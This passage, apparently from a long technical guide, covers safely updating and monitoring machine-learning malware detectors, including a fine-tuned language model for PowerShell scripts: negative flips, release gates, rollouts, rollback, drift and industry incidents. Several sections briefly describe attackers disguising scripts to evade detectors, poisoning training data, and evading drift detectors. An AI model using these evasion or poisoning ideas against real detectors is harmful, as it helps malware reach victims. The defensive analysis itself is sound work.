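On ELSA, the penalty removed about two-thirds of the security regressions and barely affected recall. On TESSERACT, it did more harm than good. For every 1,000 malicious apps from past and current periods, an average update caused about 12 fewer regressions, but the detector missed 38 more apps in total. For every 1,000 malicious apps from current and future periods, the detector missed 87 more. In the larger neural network tested on ELSA, the malware NFR fell from 7.08% to 3.35%, but recall fell from 76.33% to 63.90%.

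One likely reason is the α term, which pulls the new model towards the old one even on malware the old model missed. Ghiani and colleagues found that raising α reduced negative flips but also lowered F1, while β made little difference once α was high. A team worried about new threats could try a low α and accept more negative flips. If the team can retrain on all its old data, that looks like the better option, since in the table it gave higher recall with no more regressions.

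The penalty did better when the labels changed. In a test where each update added ten malware families, it cut the NFR from 9.76% to 7.42% and raised accuracy from 72.46% to 78.12%. *Mitigating Negative Flips via Margin Preserving Training* (2025) also focuses on updates that add classes. Its method preserves the margins by which the old model separated the classes it knew, because a slight shift can reverse a correct answer when the margin is small.

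A team could apply the same penalty to a language model's scores for "malicious" and "benign", but it would have to test for itself whether this works.

### Protecting resistance to attacks

Reducing negative flips on ordinary inputs can leave a model easier to attack. *Robustness-Congruent Adversarial Training for Secure Machine Learning Model Updates* tested this on ten updates among its seven attack-resistant image classifiers. Compared with installing the new model as is, fine-tuning it with positive-congruent training cut ordinary negative flips by an average of 1.58 percentage points but raised robustness negative flips, where an attack that used to fail now succeeds, by 11.05 points. In the worst case, the share of images an attacker could get misclassified rose from 40.65% to 84.05%.

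The penalty may not be the only cause. Angioni and colleagues fine-tuned these models on unaltered images, which can itself reduce resistance to attacks, and they did not test the same fine-tuning without the penalty. Either way, a team that fixes ordinary misses by training on ordinary scripts has to retest disguised ones.

Their own method searches for the most damaging allowed change to each training input, x′, and trains on the altered version. It minimises the sum over all examples of

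γ · L(y, f(x′)) + α · D(f(x′), f_src(x′)) + β · c · D(f(x′), f_old(x′))

Here D is half the squared distance between two models' scores, and c is 1 if the old model labels the altered input correctly and 0 if not. The model f_src is the improved model before this repair. The method therefore matches the improved model's scores in general, and the old model's scores only on altered inputs that the old model labels correctly. The weights α, β and γ add up to 1.

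This method cut ordinary flips by an average of 1.00 point and robustness flips by an average of 0.18 points over the ten updates. It avoided the damage but hardly improved resistance. Adapting it to scripts would mean searching over behaviour-preserving rewrites during training, which would take a lot of compute for a model with billions of weights. If the search used the suite's own rewrites, they would no longer be an independent test.

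### Averaging old and new weights

Some of the old behaviour can be recovered after training has finished. Schumann, Mansimov and colleagues (2023), in *Backward Compatibility During Data Updates by Weight Interpolation*, mix the two models' weights:

θ = α · θ_old + (1 − α) · θ_new

Setting α to 0 gives the new model, and setting it to 1 gives the old one. The team can try several values without retraining, and the mixed model takes no more compute to run than either original.

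The researchers tested this on RoBERTa text classifiers, in one case expanding a virtual assistant's training data from 1,000 requests to 1,500. Retraining from the pre-trained model raised accuracy from 81.8% to 83.4%, with an NFR of 3.3%. Fine-tuning the old classifier on the larger dataset gave an NFR of 2.8%, and mixing the resulting weights with the old ones lowered it to 1.4%, with accuracy still at 83.4%. Averaging 16 retrained models before mixing lowered the NFR to 0.7%. The method was less reliable when an update added new classes. On a set of news articles, the mixed model's NFR was 3.6%, compared with 3.5% for ordinary retraining.

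Mixing works well only if the new model started from the old one. When Schumann and colleagues trained the two models separately from the same pre-trained model, the weights ended up much farther apart, and most mixtures were inaccurate. The imaginary PowerShell team trained ps-12 from the base model, so it would probably have to train another candidate starting from ps-11 before using this method. With LoRA, it should average the products BA of the two adapters, because averaging A and B separately gives a different result.

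Schumann and colleagues did not test disguised or hostile inputs. A mixture could keep the old model's resistance to one disguise but lose the new model's resistance to another. The team should therefore run the suite at several values of α, choose one using the open cases, and confirm the choice on the secret ones.

### Compatibility when the base model changes

Weights from two different base models generally can't be averaged, but a new model can learn from the old one's answers. *MUSCLE*, a 2024 method from Apple, first trains an ordinary LoRA adapter for the new base model. It then continues training a copy of that adapter, called the compatibility adapter. The copy learns to match the new model's scores where it predicts the next token correctly and the old model's scores where it doesn't.

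The results depended on how much better the new base model was. These figures are for HellaSwag, a multiple-choice test of everyday situations:

| Change of base model | Accuracy, old → new | Accuracy with MUSCLE | NFR, ordinary → MUSCLE |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 1 to Llama 2 | 72.74% → 72.91% | 79.53% | 10.27% → 6.10% |
| Phi 1.5 to Phi 2 | 69.76% → 78.02% | 77.86% | 3.09% → 3.33% |
| Phi 1 to Phi 1.5 | 32.38% → 69.76% | 69.86% | 2.47% → 2.34% |

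When the two Llama models were about equally accurate, MUSCLE removed about 41% of the negative flips. Total errors fell by only about 24%, so higher accuracy alone is unlikely to explain the whole reduction. When the new model was much better, the method made almost no difference. In the update from Phi 1, it even lowered accuracy on a set of maths problems from 30.02% to 26.99%. Phi 1 had solved only 3.41% of those problems, so the new model had little to learn from it.

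The researchers did not cover updates that change the tokenizer, which splits text into tokens. Such a change makes it harder to match two models' scores token by token. They warn that the new model may inherit the old one's biases, which for a detector could include a tendency to classify certain scripts as safe. The study used general tasks and models that are now several generations old, so a security team should test MUSCLE on the team's own attacks before relying on it.

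### Starting again from an earlier version

If the training data is faulty, adding more examples may only hide the problem. Poisoned examples can affect how the model classifies scripts from a single user or machine, so a team could correct every miss it knows about and still leave others in place. It is safer to remove the suspect data and retrain from a version that was not trained on it. If the faulty model is already in use, the team first restores the previous one.

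The change record helps the team find the cause of a regression. Suppose ps-12 misses attacks that resemble backup scripts, and the team suspects the analyst corrections, most of which label a script benign. The team can train one version without the corrections and another without the new scripts from the commercial feed, using two or three random seeds for each to account for chance variation. If the misses disappear only when the corrections are absent, the team can check those labels, add malicious scripts that imitate backups, and train the next candidate from the base model.

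## Deciding whether to adopt the update

A team adopts a candidate if it passes the release gates, which are conditions the team set before testing. Gates written after seeing the results would be worth little, because a team with dozens of measures can usually find some that favour the candidate.

The simplest rule is to accept any candidate that scores higher than the current model. *BRIDGE* (Sunaryono, 2026) tested this rule on five collections of prediction tasks, some of them clinical, and checked each accepted update on data set aside from the start. Between 12.5% and 25.6% of accepted updates were no better than the model they replaced. That share was 38% to 64% when the candidate had led by half a point or less, and at most 4% when it had led by more than two points. One cause is that developers often pick the best of several candidates and then judge it on the same data, so its score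 is partly luck. Sunaryono's own rule requires a candidate to be tested on data not used to select it, and the low end of its estimated gain to exceed a fixed minimum. Under that rule, at most 1.7% of accepted updates were no better than the model they replaced. The study used conventional models and no security tasks, but its results are a good reason to distrust a half-point gain.

### Setting the gates

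The imaginary PowerShell team might write these gates for ps-12 into its change record on 1 December, before running any tests. The numbers are examples.

| Gate | Condition for ps-12 |
|---|---|
| Floor per threat family | Catches at least 90% of variants in every family, averaged by seed |
| Cap on security regressions | At most 40 of the 4,000 malicious cases, from at most three seeds in any family |
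| False-alarm budget | At most 300 false alarms a day on live scripts |
| Cases that must never fail | All 40 correct in each of five runs |
| Minimum gain | Fewer false alarms on unfamiliar backup scripts, by more than normal variation |

A floor for each family stops a gain in one family from hiding a collapse in another. *Evolving our machine learning to stop mobile bots* (Shah and Tatoris) describes a looser rule that the internet company Cloudflare used when updating a model that detects bots, or automated visitors to websites. A new version went forward if it improved on a majority of the test datasets, so it could in principle have failed badly on the rest.

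The team can set each floor slightly below the current model's usual score to allow for variation between runs. *Automated Self-Testing as a Quality Gate* (2026) describes a wider margin for a language-model application. One measure was normally 92% to 95%, and the developers set its threshold at 80%, which caused no needless rollbacks in 38 runs. That margin would be far too wide for a detector, because a fall in recall from 95% to 80% quadruples the number of missed attacks.

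A family can also lose many detections and still stay above its floor, for instance if its detection rate falls from 99% to 91%. The cap on security regressions limits such losses.

Tight limits need many labelled cases. Renggli, Karlaš and colleagues (2019), in *Continuous Integration of Machine Learning Models with ease.ml/ci*, built a system in which a team writes its conditions in advance, such as "the new model may change at most 10% of the old model's predictions". The system then calculates how many labelled examples the test needs. For a single rate, the basic formula is

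n = ln(1/δ) / (2ε²)

where ε is the allowed error and δ is the chance of exceeding it. An error of one percentage point and a δ of 0.0001 require about 46,000 examples. Renggli and colleagues considered 30,000 to 60,000 labels practical because their users could label an example in two seconds. At five minutes per script, 46,000 would take more than 3,800 hours.

Allowing an error of five points reduces the number of test cases needed to about 1,840. If the team reuses the same cases for 32 candidates and tells the developers each time whether they passed, the number rises to about 6,300, because developers can adapt the next candidate to each result.

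The false-alarm budget should start from analysts' time. Beaugnon and Chifflier (2018) point out in *Machine Learning for Computer Security* that, beyond a certain number, false alarms leave operators less time for real ones. At five minutes each, 300 false alarms a day take 25 hours. The regression suite can't measure how often the model will raise false alarms in use, because its benign scripts are meant to look suspicious. Even 2,000 ordinary benign scripts would be too few. A model with a false-positive rate of 0.3% would flag about six of them, and six is compatible with any true rate from about 0.1% to 0.65%. The team therefore has to measure the rate on live scripts.

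The list of cases that must never fail should include the attacks that would do the most damage and the harmless files that the organisation can't work without. In 2026, a Microsoft Defender update flagged root certificates as malware. Computers use these certificates to decide which websites and programs to trust. *Microsoft Defender incorrectly flagged DigiCert root certificates as malware* (Hanspal, 2026) attributes this to an error in Microsoft's detection logic. That was a signature update, but trained models make similar mistakes. TechRadar's *Microsoft fixes annoying bug which marked Adobe emails as spam* reports that a machine-learning model in Microsoft's Exchange Online email service marked legitimate messages with Adobe links as spam for two days in April 2025. Starting on 25 April, a machine-learning model in the service also quarantined mail from Gmail accounts, and Microsoft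 fixed the problem in early May, according to BornCity's *Exchange Online*.

The list has to be short because failing any one case on it blocks the update. If each case has an independent 0.5% chance of failing at random, a list of 40 will block a sound candidate 18% of the time in a single run, and a list of 500 will block it 92% of the time. Running the list five times raises the risk further, so the team should first check that the current model passes all five runs.

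A check that nobody ran should count as a failure. *The Frontier Must Grow* (2026) applies this rule to a small language model trained in repeated rounds. Its gate also rejects any candidate whose accuracy drops by more than five points on the held-out test of any earlier release.

### A candidate that gains and loses

Suppose recall on ordinary attacks rises from 95% to 97% with the candidate, while recall on disguised attacks falls from 90% to 75%. If s is the share of attacks that are disguised, overall recall in percent is

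current model: 95 − 5s

candidate: 97 − 22s

The two detection rates are equal when 17s = 2, or s = 11.8%. The candidate detects more attacks only if fewer than about 12% of them are disguised.

| Share disguised | Current model catches, of 100 attacks | Candidate catches, of 100 attacks |
|---|---|---|
| 0% | 95.0 | 97.0 |
| 6% | 94.7 | 95.7 |
| 12% | 94.4 | 94.4 |
| 30% | 93.5 | 90.4 |
| 100% | 90.0 | 75.0 |

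If the share of attacks that are disguised is close to 6%, the minimum that Apostu and colleagues give for their source, that would favour the candidate. But attackers choose the share, and once they notice that disguised scripts get through, they can disguise every script. The team's own records will tend to understate the share, because the candidate misses disguised attacks more often than undisguised ones. If 30% of attacks are disguised, they make up only 25% of those the candidate catches.

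The break-even point is also sensitive to small errors in measurement. In general it is

gain on ordinary attacks / (gain on ordinary attacks + loss on disguised attacks)

The break-even share falls from 11.8% to 6.3% if the true gain on ordinary attacks is one point instead of two, and rises to 16.7% if the gain is three points. A team that isn't sure of its two-point gain therefore can't tell which model would catch more attacks.

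The number of false alarms can change the decision. Suppose the system screens a million scripts a day, 100 of them malicious, and the update lowers the false-positive rate from 0.5% to 0.3%. False alarms fall from about 5,000 a day to about 3,000. If each takes five minutes to clear, the time analysts spend on them falls from about 417 hours a day to 250.

If the team has only 250 hours, it would leave about 40% of the current model's alerts unread. If 6% of attacks are disguised and analysts pick alerts at random, they would reach about 56 real attacks a day with the current model and 93 with the candidate. Even if every attack were disguised, they would reach 53 with the current model and 73 with the candidate.

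That comparison is unfair to the current model, because the team could raise its threshold until it also produced 3,000 false alarms. Suppose this lowered its recall to 92% on ordinary attacks and 86% on disguised ones. The candidate would then gain five points on ordinary attacks and lose 11 on disguised ones, so the two models would break even if 31% of attacks were disguised. The team should therefore compare the models at the same number of false alarms before deciding.

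### A strict rule or a weighted trade-off

A strict no-regression rule rejects any candidate that repeatably misses an attack the current model catches. The rule is easy to explain and enforce, but few updates would pass. In the Android experiments by Ghiani and colleagues, the best combination of data and training still had a malware NFR of 0.54%. At that rate, about 22 cases in a suite of 4,000 malicious cases would regress with each update.

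Delaying an update also has a downside, because a malware model's performance degrades over time, as Elastic's *Beware Steep Decline* explains. In the example with 6% of attacks disguised, the candidate catches about one more attack a day, so a month spent on repairs would mean about 30 more missed attacks. A strict rule also gives the team a reason to keep hard cases out of its test suite, since each one could block an update.

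A weighted trade-off assigns a weight to each kind of error and accepts the candidate if the weighted total falls. With 30% of attacks disguised, the candidate in the example misses about three more attacks a day but raises 2,000 fewer false alarms. The rule would favour it unless the team considered a missed attack worse than about 645 false alarms, or 54 hours of analysts' work. If every attack were disguised, the limit would be 133 false alarms, or 11 hours. Teams can adopt updates faster under this rule, but the weight they give a missed attack is largely guesswork. The rule can also accept a candidate that no longer detects an entire threat family, if it reduces other errors enough.

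The two approaches work best together. The team can be strict about the short list, set fixed limits for families and regressions, and weigh trade-offs only for candidates that meet those requirements. With a floor of 85% on disguised attacks, the team would reject the candidate in the example no matter how many false alarms it prevented. Most small, scattered losses would not delay an update.

### Trying the candidate on live scripts

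A candidate that passes the offline tests can still fail in use. The table compares four safeguards, using the example of a million scripts a day.

| Safeguard | What it can detect | Time | Cost to analysts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Silent parallel running | Changed alert volume, disagreements on real scripts, slow or missing answers | About two weeks | Checking a sample of alerts that only the candidate raises |
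| Staged release | Crashes, floods of alerts, trouble in connected tools | A few days per stage | Handling alerts from two versions |
| Alert when either model fires | Attacks that only one model catches | As long as both run | 5,000 to 8,000 false alarms a day, instead of 3,000 |
| Rollback | Nothing by itself, but it ends the harm | Minutes to a day | Reviewing scripts the candidate may have missed |

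In silent parallel running, also called shadow mode, the candidate labels every live script but only the current model raises alerts. Shah and Tatoris report that Cloudflare does this for every new bot-detection model and breaks down the results by type of bot, device, browser and customer. Analysts already review the current model's alerts, so confirming many of the attacks that the candidate misses takes no extra work. Scripts that only the candidate flags need extra review, and a daily sample of 100 takes a little over eight hours.

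In the example, 1,400 attacks would arrive in two weeks. If 6% of them (84) were disguised, the current model would catch about 76 and the candidate about 63, a large enough gap to make the team suspicious. An organisation that sees one attack a week would learn almost nothing about recall in that time and would have to rely on its regression suite. Neither organisation would discover attacks that both models miss. Processing a million scripts a day would also require about 23 copies of the candidate running continuously, at the two seconds per script that Splunk reported.

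In a staged release, a small part of the organisation switches to the candidate first. According to Microsoft's *Use safe deployment practices to safeguard and manage your environment*, the company sends monthly Defender software updates to its own employees' devices before customers' devices, and watches for false positives and faults at each stage. It recommends that customers update lower-value machines first. Detection updates can arrive several times a day, too often for the same process, so Microsoft limits them to parts of the software where an error is less likely to crash the machine. Since 2025, Microsoft has required security companies in its partner programme to release their updates gradually, according to its *The Windows Resiliency Initiative* (2025).

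A staged rollout is much better at revealing crashes than missed attacks. A first stage with 5% of the scripts would receive five attacks a day. If 6% of those attacks are disguised, the candidate's lower recall on disguised attacks would cause one extra miss about every 22 days, which probably nobody would notice. The team can compensate by keeping the current model running silently on the same scripts.

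In the example, alerting when either model fires would catch at least 97% of ordinary attacks and 90% of disguised ones. But the combined false alarms would take analysts between 417 and 667 hours a day, so the team would give up the candidate's main benefit. This arrangement makes most sense for a few weeks, while the team repairs a known weakness.

Rollback requires a way to switch versions quickly. *The Frontier Must Grow* uses an alias, a name that points to the version in use. The alias moves to a new release only if it still points to the version that the gate compared with the candidate, so nobody can release a model based on an outdated comparison. To roll back, the system moves the alias to the release from which the current one was trained. That rule would not work for the PowerShell team, which trained ps-12 from the base model and so has to name ps-11 as the version to restore.

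Restoring the old model doesn't catch the attacks that the candidate missed, so the team also has to run the old model on the scripts that arrived while the candidate was in use. If the old model was running silently all along, the team already has its labels for those scripts and can start by reviewing the ones on which the two models disagreed.

### Failed releases at OpenAI, CrowdStrike and Cloudflare

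OpenAI's *Expanding on what we missed with sycophancy* (2025) describes an update that made GPT-4o, a model in ChatGPT, sycophantic. The updated model flattered users, validated their doubts and encouraged impulsive actions. Offline tests had generally looked good, and a small group of users had seemed to like the new version. Some expert testers had felt that its behaviour was slightly off, but OpenAI had no release test for sycophancy and released the update.

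OpenAI began the rollout on Thursday 24 April 2025 and finished it the next day. By Sunday the problem was clear, and OpenAI changed the model's system prompt that night to reduce the harm. On Monday it began a full rollback, which took about 24 hours. OpenAI's early explanation was that several changes that had each looked beneficial alone may have caused the problem together.

An update to the patterns that CrowdStrike's security software uses to recognise suspicious behaviour crashed more than eight million devices on 19 July 2024, according to Computer Weekly's *CrowdStrike blames outage on content configuration update*. The update used 21 input fields, but the software supplied only 20 values. Testing missed the mismatch because all 12 automated test cases accepted any value in the last field, so the software never tried to read it (CrowdStrike, *External Technical Root Cause Analysis*,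 2024).

CrowdStrike's *Preliminary Post Incident Review (PIR)* (2024) gives three reasons for the company's confidence in the update: tests from March, trust in a checking program that turned out to have a bug, and the success of earlier updates. CrowdStrike released its main software, including its AI models, in stages, but not the patterns in this update. It withdrew the update after 78 minutes, too late for machines that had already crashed. Ten days later, about 99% of its Windows installations were online again. CrowdStrike then added staged releases, with time to collect data at each stage before the next.

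Both cases offer lessons for deciding whether to release an update to a fine-tuned detector, although neither involved one. OpenAI's product was a general chat model, and CrowdStrike's patterns were separate from its AI models. Favourable user reactions can be misleading, and the risk may be greater for a detector because analysts will welcome fewer alerts without seeing the attacks it missed. A tester's doubts should lead to more tests before release, even if the tester can't explain them. A test suite can pass every update for months if all its cases share the same gap.

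Cloudflare's bot-detection model, a security classifier, scores every web request using a file of input features that Cloudflare refreshes every few minutes. The model normally used about 60 features, but on 18 November 2025 a change to database permissions filled the file with duplicates and pushed it past a limit of 200. Cloudflare (2025) reports that its newer traffic-handling software failed and returned error pages. Its older software kept running but gave every request a bot score of zero, so customers who blocked bots would have turned away many real visitors.

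An automatic test detected a problem within three minutes, but engineers at first suspected an attack, partly because good and bad versions of the file alternated. They restored an earlier file about three hours after the errors began. Cloudflare's *Code Orange* (2026) describes the change as an automatic update to the company's classifier that skipped the gates used for software. Cloudflare now releases such files gradually, reverts them automatically if problems appear, and keeps using the old file if the new one is unreadable.

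The incident shows that a data file can need the same gates as new weights, though it is not an example of the regressions Fetterman studied, because the model had not lost any detection ability through training. A team should decide in advance what happens if no working version is available. Cloudflare lets traffic through in that case, but scripts that skip a malware detector need to go into a queue for later screening.

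### Approval and exceptions

The person who approves an update should be responsible for responding to attacks, not for training the model. Renggli and colleagues make a similar distinction between the team that sets the test and the team that builds the model, although they note that in practice the same people may do both. In the PowerShell team, the head of security operations might approve the release after the lead analyst has confirmed that the expected alerts fit the available hours. The approver should see:

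- the result of every gate, with missing tests marked as failures
- recall by threat family for both models, at the same false-alarm budget
- the scripts behind the security regressions, grouped by cause
- the break-even share and the latest estimate of how many attacks are disguised
- any doubts from testers and analysts, in their own words
- the date of the last successful trial rollback

After the sycophancy incident, OpenAI committed to explicitly approving model behaviour for each launch and to blocking launches based on testers' judgement, even when the metrics look good. A security team can do the same by letting the lead analyst or a red-team member pause a release for a fixed period, such as three days, to write test cases for a concern.

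Sometimes a team has good reason to release a candidate that fails a gate, for example because it catches an attack already in progress. The approver then records an exception instead of changing the gate. The PowerShell team's might look like this:

| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Failed gate | Floor of 90% per family; ps-12 catches 86% of disguised DownloadString scripts |
| Reason | ps-12 catches a current attack that ps-11 misses |
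| Temporary protection | ps-11 keeps running; either model can raise an alert |
| Approved by | Head of security operations, 18 December 2026 |
| Responsible for repair | Lead model engineer |
| Expires | 15 January 2027 |
| On expiry | Restore ps-11 and cover the current attack with a detection rule, unless a repaired model has passed |

Without an expiry date, a temporary exception tends to become the new standard. If nobody acts by the expiry date, the team carries out the last entry. The approver can renew an exception only after seeing new test results. A second renewal suggests that the repair is failing or the gate is unrealistic. If the gate is unrealistic, the team changes it for the next candidate before anyone sees that candidate's results.

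## Monitoring the model between updates

Release tests cover only the scripts and system the team had at the time. Correct labels for live scripts arrive late or never, so much of the monitoring after release has to work without them.

### Signals that need no labels

The system in the earlier example screens a million scripts a day, 100 of them malicious. If it catches 95 attacks and raises 3,000 false alarms, it produces 3,095 alerts a day. A new disguise that gets 20 more attacks a day past the model would lower that count to 3,075, but chance alone typically moves a daily count of that size by about 56. Even if the model missed every attack, the count would fall by only 3%.

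| Signal | What it can reveal | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Input statistics, such as script length and how often each command appears | New software, a broken log source, a very large attack | A disguise that all 100 attacks adopt, which changes its frequency by 0.01 percentage points |
| Distribution of the model's scores | A change in the weights, prompt or serving software | An attack with a confident benign score, which joins almost a million other scripts |
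| Alert volume | A flood of false alarms, or a model that has stopped answering | Almost any loss of recall when attacks are rare |
| Disagreement with another detector | Individual attacks that only one of the two catches | Attacks that both miss |

A rewritten attack that the model confidently scores as benign may not change any of the first three signals. Disagreement between the two detectors is the best chance of finding it, provided they fail in different ways. In Fetterman's tests, Llama caught all 19 variants that Foundation-Sec missed. But some attackers prepare for several detectors at once. *Trident* (2026) cites research showing that malware authors often submit drafts to public scanning services and revise them until no scanner flags them.

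Alert volume is much better for detecting false alarms. In February 2026, Microsoft's changing criteria for spotting phishing links led Exchange Online to quarantine legitimate messages, according to Windows Central's *Microsoft's Exchange Online quarantines legitimate emails mistakenly flagged as phishing* (2026). A customer that counted quarantined messages by sender might have noticed the problem quickly.

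Harmless events also move these signals. A new backup program could add 50,000 unfamiliar scripts in a day, so a shift justifies checking a sample of scripts before retraining. Splitting the counts by threat family and machine type makes them more sensitive, because a loss of 20 alerts is easier to notice in a family that normally produces 40 than in a total of 3,095.

### Estimating recall from few labels

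A random sample of 1,000 scripts from the million would contain 0.1 attacks on average. About nine in ten such samples would contain no attacks, and an analyst would need 83 hours to check each sample.

The team can instead sample most heavily where missed attacks are likely, then weight each finding by the number of scripts it represents. If a group has N scripts, and the team checks n of them at random and finds m malicious ones, the estimated number of malicious scripts in the group is

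N × m / n

Here is a month of 30 million scripts:

| Group | Scripts | Checked | Malicious | Weight | Estimate |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model raised an alert | 92,850 | 92,850 | 2,850 | 1 | 2,850 |
| No alert, but another detector objected | 2,000 | 400 | 20 | 5 | 100 |
| No alert, but the score was close to the threshold | 30,000 | 600 | 1 | 50 | 50 |
| All others | 29,875,150 | 1,000 | 0 | 29,875 | 0 |

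The model caught 2,850 of an estimated 3,000 attacks, for a recall of 95%. Without the weights, the team would count only 21 misses and put recall above 99%.

However, one more malicious script in the third group would lower the estimate to 93%. The last group is a bigger problem, because finding nothing in 1,000 scripts can't rule out a true rate as high as about 0.3%, or some 90,000 missed attacks, though nobody would expect that many. The team should describe the 95% as recall among attacks that left some trace, either a score near the threshold or a flag from another detector.

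Planted test cases let the team measure recall even when real attacks are scarce. The team runs copies of attack scripts on a test machine, with a harmless file in place of the real download, and checks whether alerts reach the analysts. This tests the whole path from logging to alert. If the system catches 90 of 100 planted cases, its true recall on such cases is probably between 82% and 95%. The team has to mark the cases so that nobody counts them as real attacks or trains the model on them. Planted cases test only disguises that the team already knows.

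Past incidents show how the model handles attacks the team did not invent. Suppose investigators confirmed 40 attacks through user reports, network logs and other evidence independent of the model, and the model had flagged 34 of them. Its recall is 85%, with a 95% confidence interval of about 70% to 94%. Incidents that began with the model's own alert don't belong in this count, because the model caught all of them by definition.

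Investigators can take months to find the attacks a model missed, so the figure for November may still be changing in March. To compare two months fairly, the team can use what it knew 60 days after the end of each. Otherwise the latest month will usually look better than it was, because investigators have had less time to find its missed attacks.

### Replaying the suite against the live system

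A regression suite is also useful after release. The PowerShell team might run 500 of the suite's cases through the live system every night, which takes about 17 minutes at Splunk's speed, and all 6,000 every weekend. The team would then compare the answers with those from the release test. Because the cases are fixed, any difference beyond normal variation comes from a change in the system, not from new attacks.

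Anthropic's *A postmortem of three recent issues* details the 2025 misrouting that Chishti and colleagues cite, the kind of fault replay is meant to catch. On 5 August, the company's system began sending about 0.8% of Claude Sonnet 4 requests to servers configured for much longer inputs. A routine load-balancing change on 29 August increased the share, which peaked at 16% during one hour on 31 August.

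Two other faults began in late August. One occasionally put Thai or Chinese characters into answers to English questions. The other could drop the most probable token, but only with certain batch sizes and settings, so the same prompt might work once and fail the next time. A detector that answers with a single word could give the wrong label if its most probable token were dropped.

Users noticed the decline before Anthropic understood it. The company's evaluations missed the problem, partly because the model often recovers from isolated mistakes. Anthropic has since promised to run quality evaluations continuously on its production systems.

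The routing fault would have been hard to detect by replay at first. In early August, about 48 of 6,000 cases would have gone to the wrong servers. If a tenth of those had received a different label, the team would have seen about five changed labels, which is easy to mistake for normal variation. At the misrouting rate of the worst hour, it would have seen about 96. The team can improve its chances of detecting such a fault by spreading the cases over the day and adding up small differences over several nights.

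The replay also has to use the same interface as real work. In 2026, three changes made Anthropic's programming tool Claude Code perform worse: a lower default setting for reasoning effort, a bug that kept deleting the model's earlier reasoning, and a prompt instruction to keep answers short. According to Anthropic's *An update on recent Claude Code quality reports*, the API, which connects other software to the models, was unaffected, so a customer that tested only through the API would have found nothing wrong. Weeks of internal testing had also shown no regression from the prompt instruction, but a broader set of evaluations later showed a 3% drop on one evaluation.

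Cheaper checks can run between full replays. Chauvin and colleagues ran hourly checks that requested only the probabilities of a single token and cost $0.14 a year, compared with $146 and $332 for two other methods. Of the 37 changes they suspected, 34 affected models with openly published weights, so choosing an open model doesn't guarantee that a supplier will serve it unchanged. *Behavioral Fingerprints for LLM Endpoint Stability and Identity* (2026) describes a check that needs only ordinary text answers, replaying a fixed set of prompts until there is enough evidence of a change to act on. These checks show that a model has changed, but not whether it catches fewer attacks, so the team should follow an alarm with a full replay.

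### How quickly detectors age

Many published scores don't show how much a detector's performance declines over time. In *TESSERACT*, Pendlebury, Pierazzi and colleagues (2018) traced inflated results for Android malware detectors to two causes. Some researchers had trained their models on apps newer than those in the test, which gave the models information they wouldn't have in real use, and some tests contained an unrealistic share of malware. Kan, McFadden and colleagues (2024) extended the study to 259,230 apps, training on those from 2014 and testing on those from the next four years. They found that well-known detectors could perform up to 50% worse in practice than in the biased tests.

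A time-ordered test trains only on samples older than the test samples and keeps a realistic share of malware in each period. The TESSERACT researchers summarise the results in a measure called area under time (AUT), which *DRMD* (2025) gives as

AUT = [1 / (N − 1)] × Σ (Pₖ + Pₖ₊₁) / 2

where Pₖ is the performance in period k, N is the number of periods, and the sum runs over neighbouring periods. If F1 is 0.9, 0.8, 0.6 and 0.5 in four successive quarters, AUT is (0.85 + 0.70 + 0.55) / 3 = 0.70. A team should look at the quarterly figures too, because a detector that scored 0.7 throughout would have the same AUT.

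In *EXE-Bench*, Ponte, Gibert and colleagues (2026) trained 30 Windows malware detectors on files from 2017 or earlier and tested them on files dated 2019 to 2022. They averaged F1 over time periods, giving more weight to periods with more files. *Moirae* (2026) reports tests of Android detectors trained on apps from 2011 to 2016.

| Detector | Early result | Later result |
|---|---|---|
| Decision trees, Windows | F1 of 0.99 on held-out files | 0.78 on files from 2019–2022 |
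| MalConv, a neural network, Windows | F1 of 0.99 on held-out files | 0.52 on files from 2019–2022 |
| CL-Malware, Android | 92.5% accuracy in 2017 | 61.5% in 2021 |

MalConv did just as well as the decision trees on the held-out test, but the decision trees did best on the later files. A team choosing between the two by held-out score could not have predicted this difference.

Age may not explain the whole decline. Ponte and colleagues took the later Windows files from a different collection and relied on dates inside the files, which malware authors can forge. The F1 of their most durable models rose and fell from one period to the next, with no steady decline, so a team can't use these results to set a reliable expiry date for a model.

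Moirae's own system, which runs each app and needs no fine-tuning, kept an accuracy of about 87% to 92% through 2021, but its recall fell to about 77% in the last year. The test was not time-ordered if the system's underlying model learned from data collected after 2021.

Detectors of malicious web domains also become less accurate over time. Some malware uses an algorithm to generate large numbers of domain names, through which it contacts its operators. *DRIFT* (2026) tested three detectors of such names on data up to 2025, and all three missed far more of them as the time between training and testing grew. Most of this evidence comes from decision trees and specialised neural networks, so a fine-tuned language model may lose accuracy at a different rate.

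Retraining can restore much of the lost performance. In *Is It Overkill?*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues retrained an Android detector every month on the previous three months of apps. Its F1 stayed high from 2015 to 2021, while that of an unchanged detector fell. The retrained detector did as well with the list of app characteristics chosen in early 2015 as with a list updated every month, so for these detectors, fresh examples mattered more than an updated list. The researchers assumed that plenty of correct labels were available, which is rarely true in daily use.

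### How drift detectors choose inputs to reject

Some drift detectors track the model's errors. *Adversarial Evasion in Non-Stationary Malware Detection* (2026) describes two classic methods, one that monitors the error rate and one that monitors the spacing between errors. Both need correct labels soon after the model makes its predictions. If analysts label only alerts, these methods will count false alarms but not missed attacks.

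Other drift detectors look for inputs unlike the training data. Transcend compares a new script with the training scripts in each class. If 30 of 1,000 benign training scripts are at least as unusual for that class as the new one, the new script's p-value for "benign" is 0.03. Suppose its p-value for "malicious" is 0.01 and the model labels it benign. Transcend then calculates

credibility = p-value for the predicted class = 0.03

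confidence = 1 − highest p-value for any other class = 0.99

The product is about 0.03, which marks the script as unfamiliar. A routine administrative script with p-values of 0.60 and 0.01 would score 0.59. *Drift-Aware Explainable Prioritization for Windows PE Malware Forensic Triage* (2026) describes how Transcend and its successor, Transcendent, withhold a label when the score is too low. The team can then send the script to an analyst.

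CADE, another drift detector, trains a neural network to represent each input as a point, with inputs of the same class close together. It measures how far a new input is from the centre of each class and compares that distance with what is typical for the class. CADE flags the input as drifting if it is unusually far from every class.

Rejection helps only if someone can check the rejected scripts. Setting aside the least familiar 1% of a million scripts a day would create 10,000 daily reviews, or 833 hours of work. Neither method would reject a disguised attack that closely resembles routine administration, because it would look familiar.

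### Attacks on drift detectors

*Empirical Analysis of Evasion and Poisoning Against Malware Data Drift Detection* (Yang, Lie and Papernot, 2026), a University of Toronto study, tested attacks meant to fool a malware classifier and a drift detector together, using one collection of Windows files and one of Android apps. An analyst would check the 500 most unusual files from a month, so an attack succeeded only if the classifier called the malware benign and the drift detector left it out of those 500.

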